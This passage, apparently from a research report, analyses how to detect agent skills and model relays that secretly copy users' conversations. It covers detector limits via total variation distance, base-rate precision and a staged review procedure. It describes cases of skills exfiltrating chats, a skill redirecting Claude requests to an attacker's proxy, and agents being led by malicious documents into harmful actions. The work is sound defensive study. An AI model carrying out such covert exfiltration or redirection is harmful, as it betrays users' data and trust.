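The table applies these methods to two cases. In the first, a document-formatting skill secretly uploads the conversation. In the second, a skill openly relays messages through a proxy whose operator secretly keeps copies. The entries are predictions based on how each method works, not test results.

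| Method | Hidden collector | Proxy that keeps copies |
|---|---|---|
| Traffic size and timing | May show an extra upload with little data coming back | Shows a normal request and reply |
| Elastic's rule for unfamiliar domains | Alerts if a listed program on a Mac contacts a new domain | May alert on first use, as it would for an honest proxy |
| Agent Detector | Probably reports the agent but not the collector | May report the proxy, as it would an honest one |
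| Fake credentials and human review | Catches the upload if it includes a fake credential and happens during the test | Shows a transfer that matches the description |
| SkillSentry | Catches the upload if a test triggers it | Shows a transfer that the advertised task requires |

SkillSentry should also catch some cases between these two. If a relay skill sent a second copy to another server, that transfer would appear only with the skill, and the user wouldn't need it to get a reply. SkillSentry should also catch Plan Refine, which redirected Claude requests to an attacker's proxy. The agent contacts a model with or without the skill, but SkillSentry counts a change of destination as a new effect, and improving a plan doesn't require changing the destination.

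None of the methods would catch the proxy operator unless somebody sent a canary through the proxy. SkillSentry might not contact the operator's real server, because it uses a language model to simulate the environment.

A skill's author can also add a collector in an update after the skill has passed its tests. Network monitoring might detect the new server, though Elastic's rule would miss it if a Python script sent the data. Testing every update would be more thorough, but SkillSentry took about two minutes and 190,000 input tokens per skill on SkillTrustBench. SkillSpector's fixed rules took just over two seconds and used no tokens.

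## Which signals separate theft from normal use

Network monitors and sandboxes can't show a reviewer everything they need to know, such as who chose a server or what its owner does with the data. The table compares earlier cases by seven signals. A reviewer who relied on any one signal would judge one of the cases correctly and another incorrectly.

| Signal | What suggests theft | A case it settles | A case it gets wrong |
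|---|---|---|---|
| Who chose the destination | Someone other than the user or employer chose it | Plan Refine sent users' Claude requests to a server they hadn't picked | Researchers picked 17 free routers themselves, and someone still used the AWS keys they had planted |
| Whether the user was told | The software hides or denies the transfer | SecondBrain's store listing said it collected no data | Urban VPN disclosed its collection of chats in its privacy policy |
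| Whether the program uses the reply | It ignores the reply | The AITOPIA look-alikes uploaded chats and needed nothing back | An honest backup extension needs nothing back either |
| Whether there is a second recipient | Another server gets a copy | Two ad blockers copied messages that the chatbot had already received | Intruders copied prompts inside three model hosts, where the client couldn't see them |
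| Whether the program sends more than the task needs | It sends unrelated data | Urban VPN copied chats even with the VPN off | Ana's coding agent sends her database password again with every request |
| Whether unrelated publishers share the destination | They all use the same obscure server | Five groups of skills led to attacker-controlled domains | Thousands of honest skills contact OpenAI or OpenRouter |
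| What the recipient does afterwards | It uses or sells the data | Someone emptied a planted cryptocurrency wallet | MiniMax's security monitoring visited web addresses from prompts automatically |

Three of these signals can be falsely reassuring: the user chose the server, the software disclosed the transfer, and only one recipient is visible. The other four signals in the table can instead raise false alarms.

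Signals work better together if they depend on different facts. Urban VPN looks acceptable if judged only on whether it disclosed the collection, but a VPN doesn't need chats. An ignored reply and a second recipient often have the same cause, because a program that copies a chat to a collector rarely needs an answer. Counting them separately would exaggerate the case against a backup extension.

Disclosure is also a weaker signal than it seems. Users approve a whole skill at once, and it can then read files and open network connections without asking again. Liu and colleagues, who built SkillScan, use the term "consent gap" for the difference between what users approve and what a skill does.

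A skill that sends too much can be hard to spot if its author never says what it should send. ClawHub raised a concern about a skill that contacts a remote agent at an address the user supplies, because what it sends is neither limited nor justified. The user's agent could also call the skill without an explicit request. Relay To Agent is easier to assess because its history is limited to 50 messages.

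A relay's behaviour can change within weeks, so evidence about a recipient can go out of date. Wu and colleagues compared relays' answers with those of the official models, then repeated the test 11 to 18 days later on 35 combinations of relay and model. Seven combinations gained or lost a flag for unusual answers. The four relays that had returned forbidden tool calls in the first round returned none in the second.

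A low price is also weak evidence of theft. Wu and colleagues flagged seven of ten cheap relays for unusual answers, compared with two of ten that charged the official price or more. With only 20 relays, this difference could be chance (*p* = 0.07), and an unusual answer doesn't show that anyone kept the conversation.

### The limit on any detector

Any detector's ability to separate theft from normal use has a mathematical limit, which depends on how much the two differ in the data the detector receives.

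Let *P* be the distribution of what the detector observes when a program is malicious, and *Q* the distribution when it is harmless. The total variation distance between them is the largest difference between the probabilities they give to the same set of observations *A*:

TV(*P*, *Q*) = max |*P*(*A*) − *Q*(*A*)| = ½ Σ |*P*(*x*) − *Q*(*x*)|

The maximum is over all sets *A*, and the sum is over all observations *x*. The distance is 0 if the distributions are identical and 1 if they do not overlap.

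If a detector flags every observation in a set *A*, its true-positive rate (its recall) is *P*(*A*) and its false-positive rate is *Q*(*A*). The difference between them can't exceed the largest difference for any set, so:

true-positive rate − false-positive rate ≤ TV(*P*, *Q*)

This is a standard result in hypothesis testing. *On the Privacy Properties of GAN-generated Samples* (2022) uses it to limit attacks on the privacy of AI-generated data, and *AI Detectors Fail Diverse Student Populations* (Garland, 2026) applies it to software that tries to recognise AI-written essays.

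Here is an example with invented numbers. The detector sees only where a program sends a conversation and whether it uses the reply:

| Observation | Malicious programs | Harmless programs | Difference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Address from the user's settings, reply used | 20% | 70% | −50 points |
| Any other address, reply used | 30% | 20% | +10 points |
| Any other address, reply ignored | 50% | 10% | +40 points |

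The distance is ½(0.5 + 0.1 + 0.4) = 0.5, so no detector using these observations, however sophisticated, can have a gap of more than 50 points between the percentage of malicious programs it flags and the percentage of harmless ones. A detector that flags every address from outside the user's settings reaches this limit, flagging 80% of malicious programs and 30% of harmless ones. One that flags only ignored replies finds 50% of malicious programs and flags 10% of harmless ones, a difference of 40 points.

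Suppose one proxy operator secretly keeps copies and another doesn't, but both pass on requests and replies in the same way. The client then sees the same distribution from both, so the distance is zero, and a detector that catches 90% of the dishonest operators must also flag 90% of the honest ones. Watching for longer doesn't help. Garland cites earlier work showing that reliable detection at a distance of δ takes on the order of 1/δ² independent samples, a number that grows without limit as δ approaches zero.

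A real operator may be less careful and, for example, add a delay when it saves a conversation. The limit is zero only if everything the client can observe stays the same.

Garland's argument also explains why honest proxy users can get most of the false alarms. For any group of harmless programs, the false-positive rate is at least the detector's true-positive rate minus the distance between that group and the malicious programs. Suppose clients for private company proxies are at a distance of 0.2 from malicious programs. A detector that finds 90% of the malicious programs must then flag at least 70% of these clients. If they make up 5% of harmless programs, flagging 70% of them adds only 3.5 percentage points to the overall false-positive rate. The detector could therefore look accurate on average but be almost useless to companies with their own gateways.

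The best possible detector may fall far below this limit when false positives have to be very rare. *Closed-Form Noise Calibration Against Membership Inference for Random-Allocation DP-SGD* (2026) gives an example from a different field, tests of whether a model's training data included a particular record. With a distance of 0.1 and a false-positive rate of 0.1%, the limit allows a true-positive rate of 10.1%, but the best possible test reached only about 0.2%. This gap matters for marketplace scanners because even a small false-positive rate produces many false alarms among more than 100,000 skills.

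### How added facts raise the limit

A detector can do better if it learns something new. Song, Cuff and Poor (2014), in *A Rate-Distortion Based Secrecy System with Side Information at the Decoders*, list two properties of total variation distance that explain when this works. Adding an observation never reduces the distance:

```
TV(traffic alone) ≤ TV(traffic and added fact)
```

However, the distance stays the same if the added fact depends on the traffic in the same way for malicious and harmless programs. For example, running a second pattern rule on the same line of code may help a poor detector get closer to the limit, but it doesn't change the limit, because the rule's result depends only on code the detector already had.

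A canary can provide new evidence by testing what happens after the recipient gets the conversation. Suppose somebody uses a planted key within a month at 20% of dishonest proxies and 0.1% of honest ones. The client's traffic is identical in both cases, but the statistical distance between the two groups rises from zero to 0.199. Flagging every proxy where someone uses the key would catch a fifth of the dishonest operators with very few false alarms, but the rest would still look honest.

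Knowing what is authorised can be even more useful, because exfiltration is by definition unauthorised. If Ana's employer has approved one proxy and forbidden all others, sending company code to another proxy is exfiltration, even if the request differs from an approved one only in its address and key. Checking the address against a list of approved servers can reveal this immediately.

Attestation, which lets a client verify what code a proxy is running, mainly helps to clear honest operators. Suppose 5% of honest operators can prove that the code they run keeps no conversations, and no dishonest operator can. The distance rises only to 0.05, because the other 95% still look the same as dishonest operators. Xie and colleagues make a similar point about their own design. Ana can trust an attested proxy more, but she can't conclude much about an unattested one until more honest operators adopt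 attestation.

### Four thefts among 134,934 skills

Even an accurate signal produces mostly false alarms when theft is rare. Etteib and colleagues found four skills that secretly monitored conversations among the 134,934 they scanned. Four is the number they found, not an estimate of how many there were. Assume, for illustration, that 1% of the skills (1,349) legitimately call outside models, and that a simple rule flags all of these and all four thefts:

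| Rule | Thefts flagged | Honest skills flagged | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flag every skill that calls an outside model | 4 | 1,349 | 0.3% |
| Also require a signal with 95% recall and 2% false positives | 3.8 | 27 | 12% |
| Also require a second, independent signal that is just as good | 3.6 | 0.5 | 87% |

A signal that flagged 95% of thefts and only 2% of honest skills would be excellent, but because thefts are rare, about seven of every eight flags would still be false alarms. Such a signal could exist only if the total variation distance between thefts and honest skills were at least 0.93, the difference between the two rates.

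A precision of 12% is poor for automatic blocking but useful for choosing what to review. At SkillScan's pace of 15 to 30 minutes per skill, one person could check the 31 remaining skills in about 8 to 15 hours. Checking all 1,353 would take 338 to 677 hours.

The third row holds only if the signals are independent. Two rules triggered by the same web address would mostly flag the same honest skills, so precision would stay much closer to 12%. A better pair might be an unexplained second recipient and an obscure server shared by unrelated publishers.

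Precision would also be higher if the scan missed some thefts. With 40 thefts and the same 1,349 honest skills, precision would be 2.9% under the simple rule and 58% with the first additional signal.

### A review procedure

These results suggest starting with checks that take little effort and add new facts, then having people review the cases that remain. In the procedure below, "ask" means asking the data's owner, who may be the user's employer. "Investigate" means holding the software back while someone collects more evidence.

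| Step | Check | Rough cost | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Look up every destination in the owner's list of approved servers | Seconds | Allow if all are approved and the network blocks the rest |
| 2 | Compare the description with the destination and the data | A few minutes | Block if the software hides the transfer, or if its author chose a recipient the task doesn't need. Ask if the transfer is disclosed but the owner hasn't approved the recipient |
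| 3 | Search other publishers' software for the same address | A few minutes | Investigate if unrelated publishers share an obscure server |
| 4 | Run the task with fake credentials, with and without the software | About two minutes and 190,000 tokens with SkillSentry | Block if an unexplained transfer appears |
| 5 | Have a person read the code and look into the publisher | 15 to 30 minutes | Allow, ask or block |
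| 6 | Send canaries through the recipient | Weeks | Block and investigate if somebody uses one |

The reviewer stops at the first step that leads to a decision. If, at step 2, the owner knows who runs the server and agrees to the transfer, the reviewer can allow it. If the owner doesn't know, the reviewer should go on to step 3. Permission should cover only the named server, and the network should still block others where possible.

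If a sandbox test at step 4 gives an unclear result, a person needs to interpret it. Liu and colleagues report running 25 skills that SkillScan had flagged with high confidence, although their paper's ethics statement contradicts this by saying that the team ran no potentially malicious skills. Eighteen did what the scanner had predicted, four gave inconclusive results, and three were legitimate security tools. Blocking all 25 automatically would have stopped at least three legitimate tools.

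An unused canary at step 6 isn't a reason to allow a recipient. Wu and colleagues assume that a relay may behave differently when it recognises a test, so canaries should look like ordinary secrets in ordinary requests. They make more sense for a router that a whole company uses every day than for a skill that one person wants to try.

The reviewer should also repeat the checks whenever the software, the address or the server's owner changes. *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* (2026) describes two malicious versions of LiteLLM, a popular gateway program, that were released in March 2026 and collected credentials and cryptocurrency wallets. If a company had approved LiteLLM on its own server and then installed one of these versions, its traffic would still have gone to the approved address.

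### Relay To Agent

The reviewer can't finish step 1 for Relay To Agent until the user chooses an endpoint. If Ana sets the base URL to her employer's approved gateway, the reviewer can allow that destination. In an earlier review, ClawHub advised users to set `RELAY_BASE_URL` themselves instead of relying on the supplied configuration file, and to check that file for unexpected agents.

At step 2, the description matches the transfer, so the reviewer should ask the data's owner who runs the chosen server and whether that operator may receive these conversations. SkillSpector's External Transmission findings don't help answer either question.

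The owner can agree on conditions that reduce the possible damage. ClawHub recommends a key with limited permissions. Its May audit also suggests using `--reset` before an unrelated task, so the new recipient doesn't get old messages it doesn't need.

The file-path bug needs a separate decision, because the owner hasn't agreed to send unrelated files. Someone who uses only the default session name could reasonably accept the risk. A company should wait for a fix if an agent can choose the session name, because a malicious web page or document might lead the agent to choose a harmful one.

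The reviewer can therefore allow the skill with those conditions if the endpoint is approved. If nobody can identify the server, the reviewer could continue to steps 3 to 5, but the results would probably look normal whether or not the operator is honest. Allowing the skill would be inappropriate in that case if the conversations contain company code.

### The SOCKS5 stock-analysis skill

The stock-analysis skill has two destinations: the market-data service and the proxy that carries requests to it. A reviewer who looks up only the market-data service at step 1 could approve the skill by mistake. The reviewer also needs to look up the proxy, whose address is in the skill's text. An unknown server wouldn't be on the list.

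The reviewer can decide at step 2. Fetching stock prices doesn't normally require a proxy, the author chose this one, and nothing in the skill's advertised purpose explains it. The reviewer should block the skill as written.

Blocking a connection needs less evidence than accusing its author of theft, because it doesn't require proof that the author is a thief and not just careless. Garland argues that universities shouldn't use a detector's score as the only evidence of misconduct, and the same caution makes sense before accusing an author of theft.

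A user who wants the skill could delete the proxy setting and see whether the skill still works. If it does, it didn't need the proxy. If the market-data service blocks the user's region, the user could supply a proxy they trust. A marketplace would have more reason to investigate than a single user, because it could search for the same server in other publishers' skills and warn everyone who had installed them.

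### The case for blocking by default

Some transfers will remain unclear after every practical check, so a company or marketplace needs a default for handling them. The SkillScan paper recommends blocking dangerous patterns regardless of the author's apparent intent. The study often couldn't determine whether a high-risk skill was carelessly written or malicious, and a user's data can leak either way.

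Blocking also makes sense because nobody can take back a stolen transcript, and an unknown router could change the commands that an agent runs.

Liu and colleagues also want each skill to declare the access it needs and the platform to enforce those limits. A declaration would help only if it were specific. One of their examples of excessive permissions is a code-formatting skill that requests access to every server on the two standard web ports. Relay To Agent's server can't be known in advance, so the platform would have to let the user fill it in.

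Blocking every skill that calls an outside model would mainly harm honest developers and users. Under the earlier assumption, it would stop about 337 honest skills for each theft found. New publishers and people who run their own servers would probably suffer most, because their addresses are unfamiliar. Some users would also move to personal computers or other tools that nobody monitors.

### The case for allowing with disclosure

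The user often knows what the scanner can't find out, such as whether an unfamiliar address belongs to their employer, and disclosure lets them use that knowledge. ClawHub's *Agent Relay* audit takes this approach with a skill that lets an outside relay deliver messages to the user's agent. It advises people to install the skill only if they trust the relay's operator or run the relay themselves. It also recommends treating incoming messages as requests, not commands, and checking that the connection can be switched off.

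This approach keeps unusual but honest tools available and lets people try a new provider without waiting for approval. However, some users will ignore the warning and have their conversations stolen. Others will read it carefully and still have no way to check the operator. An employee may also agree to send data that belongs to their employer or a customer.

A simple calculation shows how the choice depends on the costs. Let *p* be the probability that a flagged skill is a theft, *L* the loss if it is allowed, and *C* the cost of blocking an honest skill. Blocking is better if:

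*pL* > (1 − *p*)*C*

Under the simple rule from the base-rate example, blocking a flagged skill is worthwhile only if a theft does more than 337 times as much harm as blocking an honest skill. With the additional signal, the required ratio falls to about seven. The calculation assumes that the harm doesn't vary from one theft to another or from one mistaken block to another. In practice it does, so a hospital's patient conversations should have a different threshold from a hobbyist's recipe chats.

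Blocking is the better default for hidden transfers, and for recipients that the author chose and the task doesn't need. It is also better when an unknown recipient would get company code or medical data, as long as someone can quickly approve an honest server. For less sensitive conversations, disclosure is reasonable if the user chooses the endpoint and the software names it before the first transfer. The software should ask again when the address changes, but not on every message, because users would soon stop reading the question.
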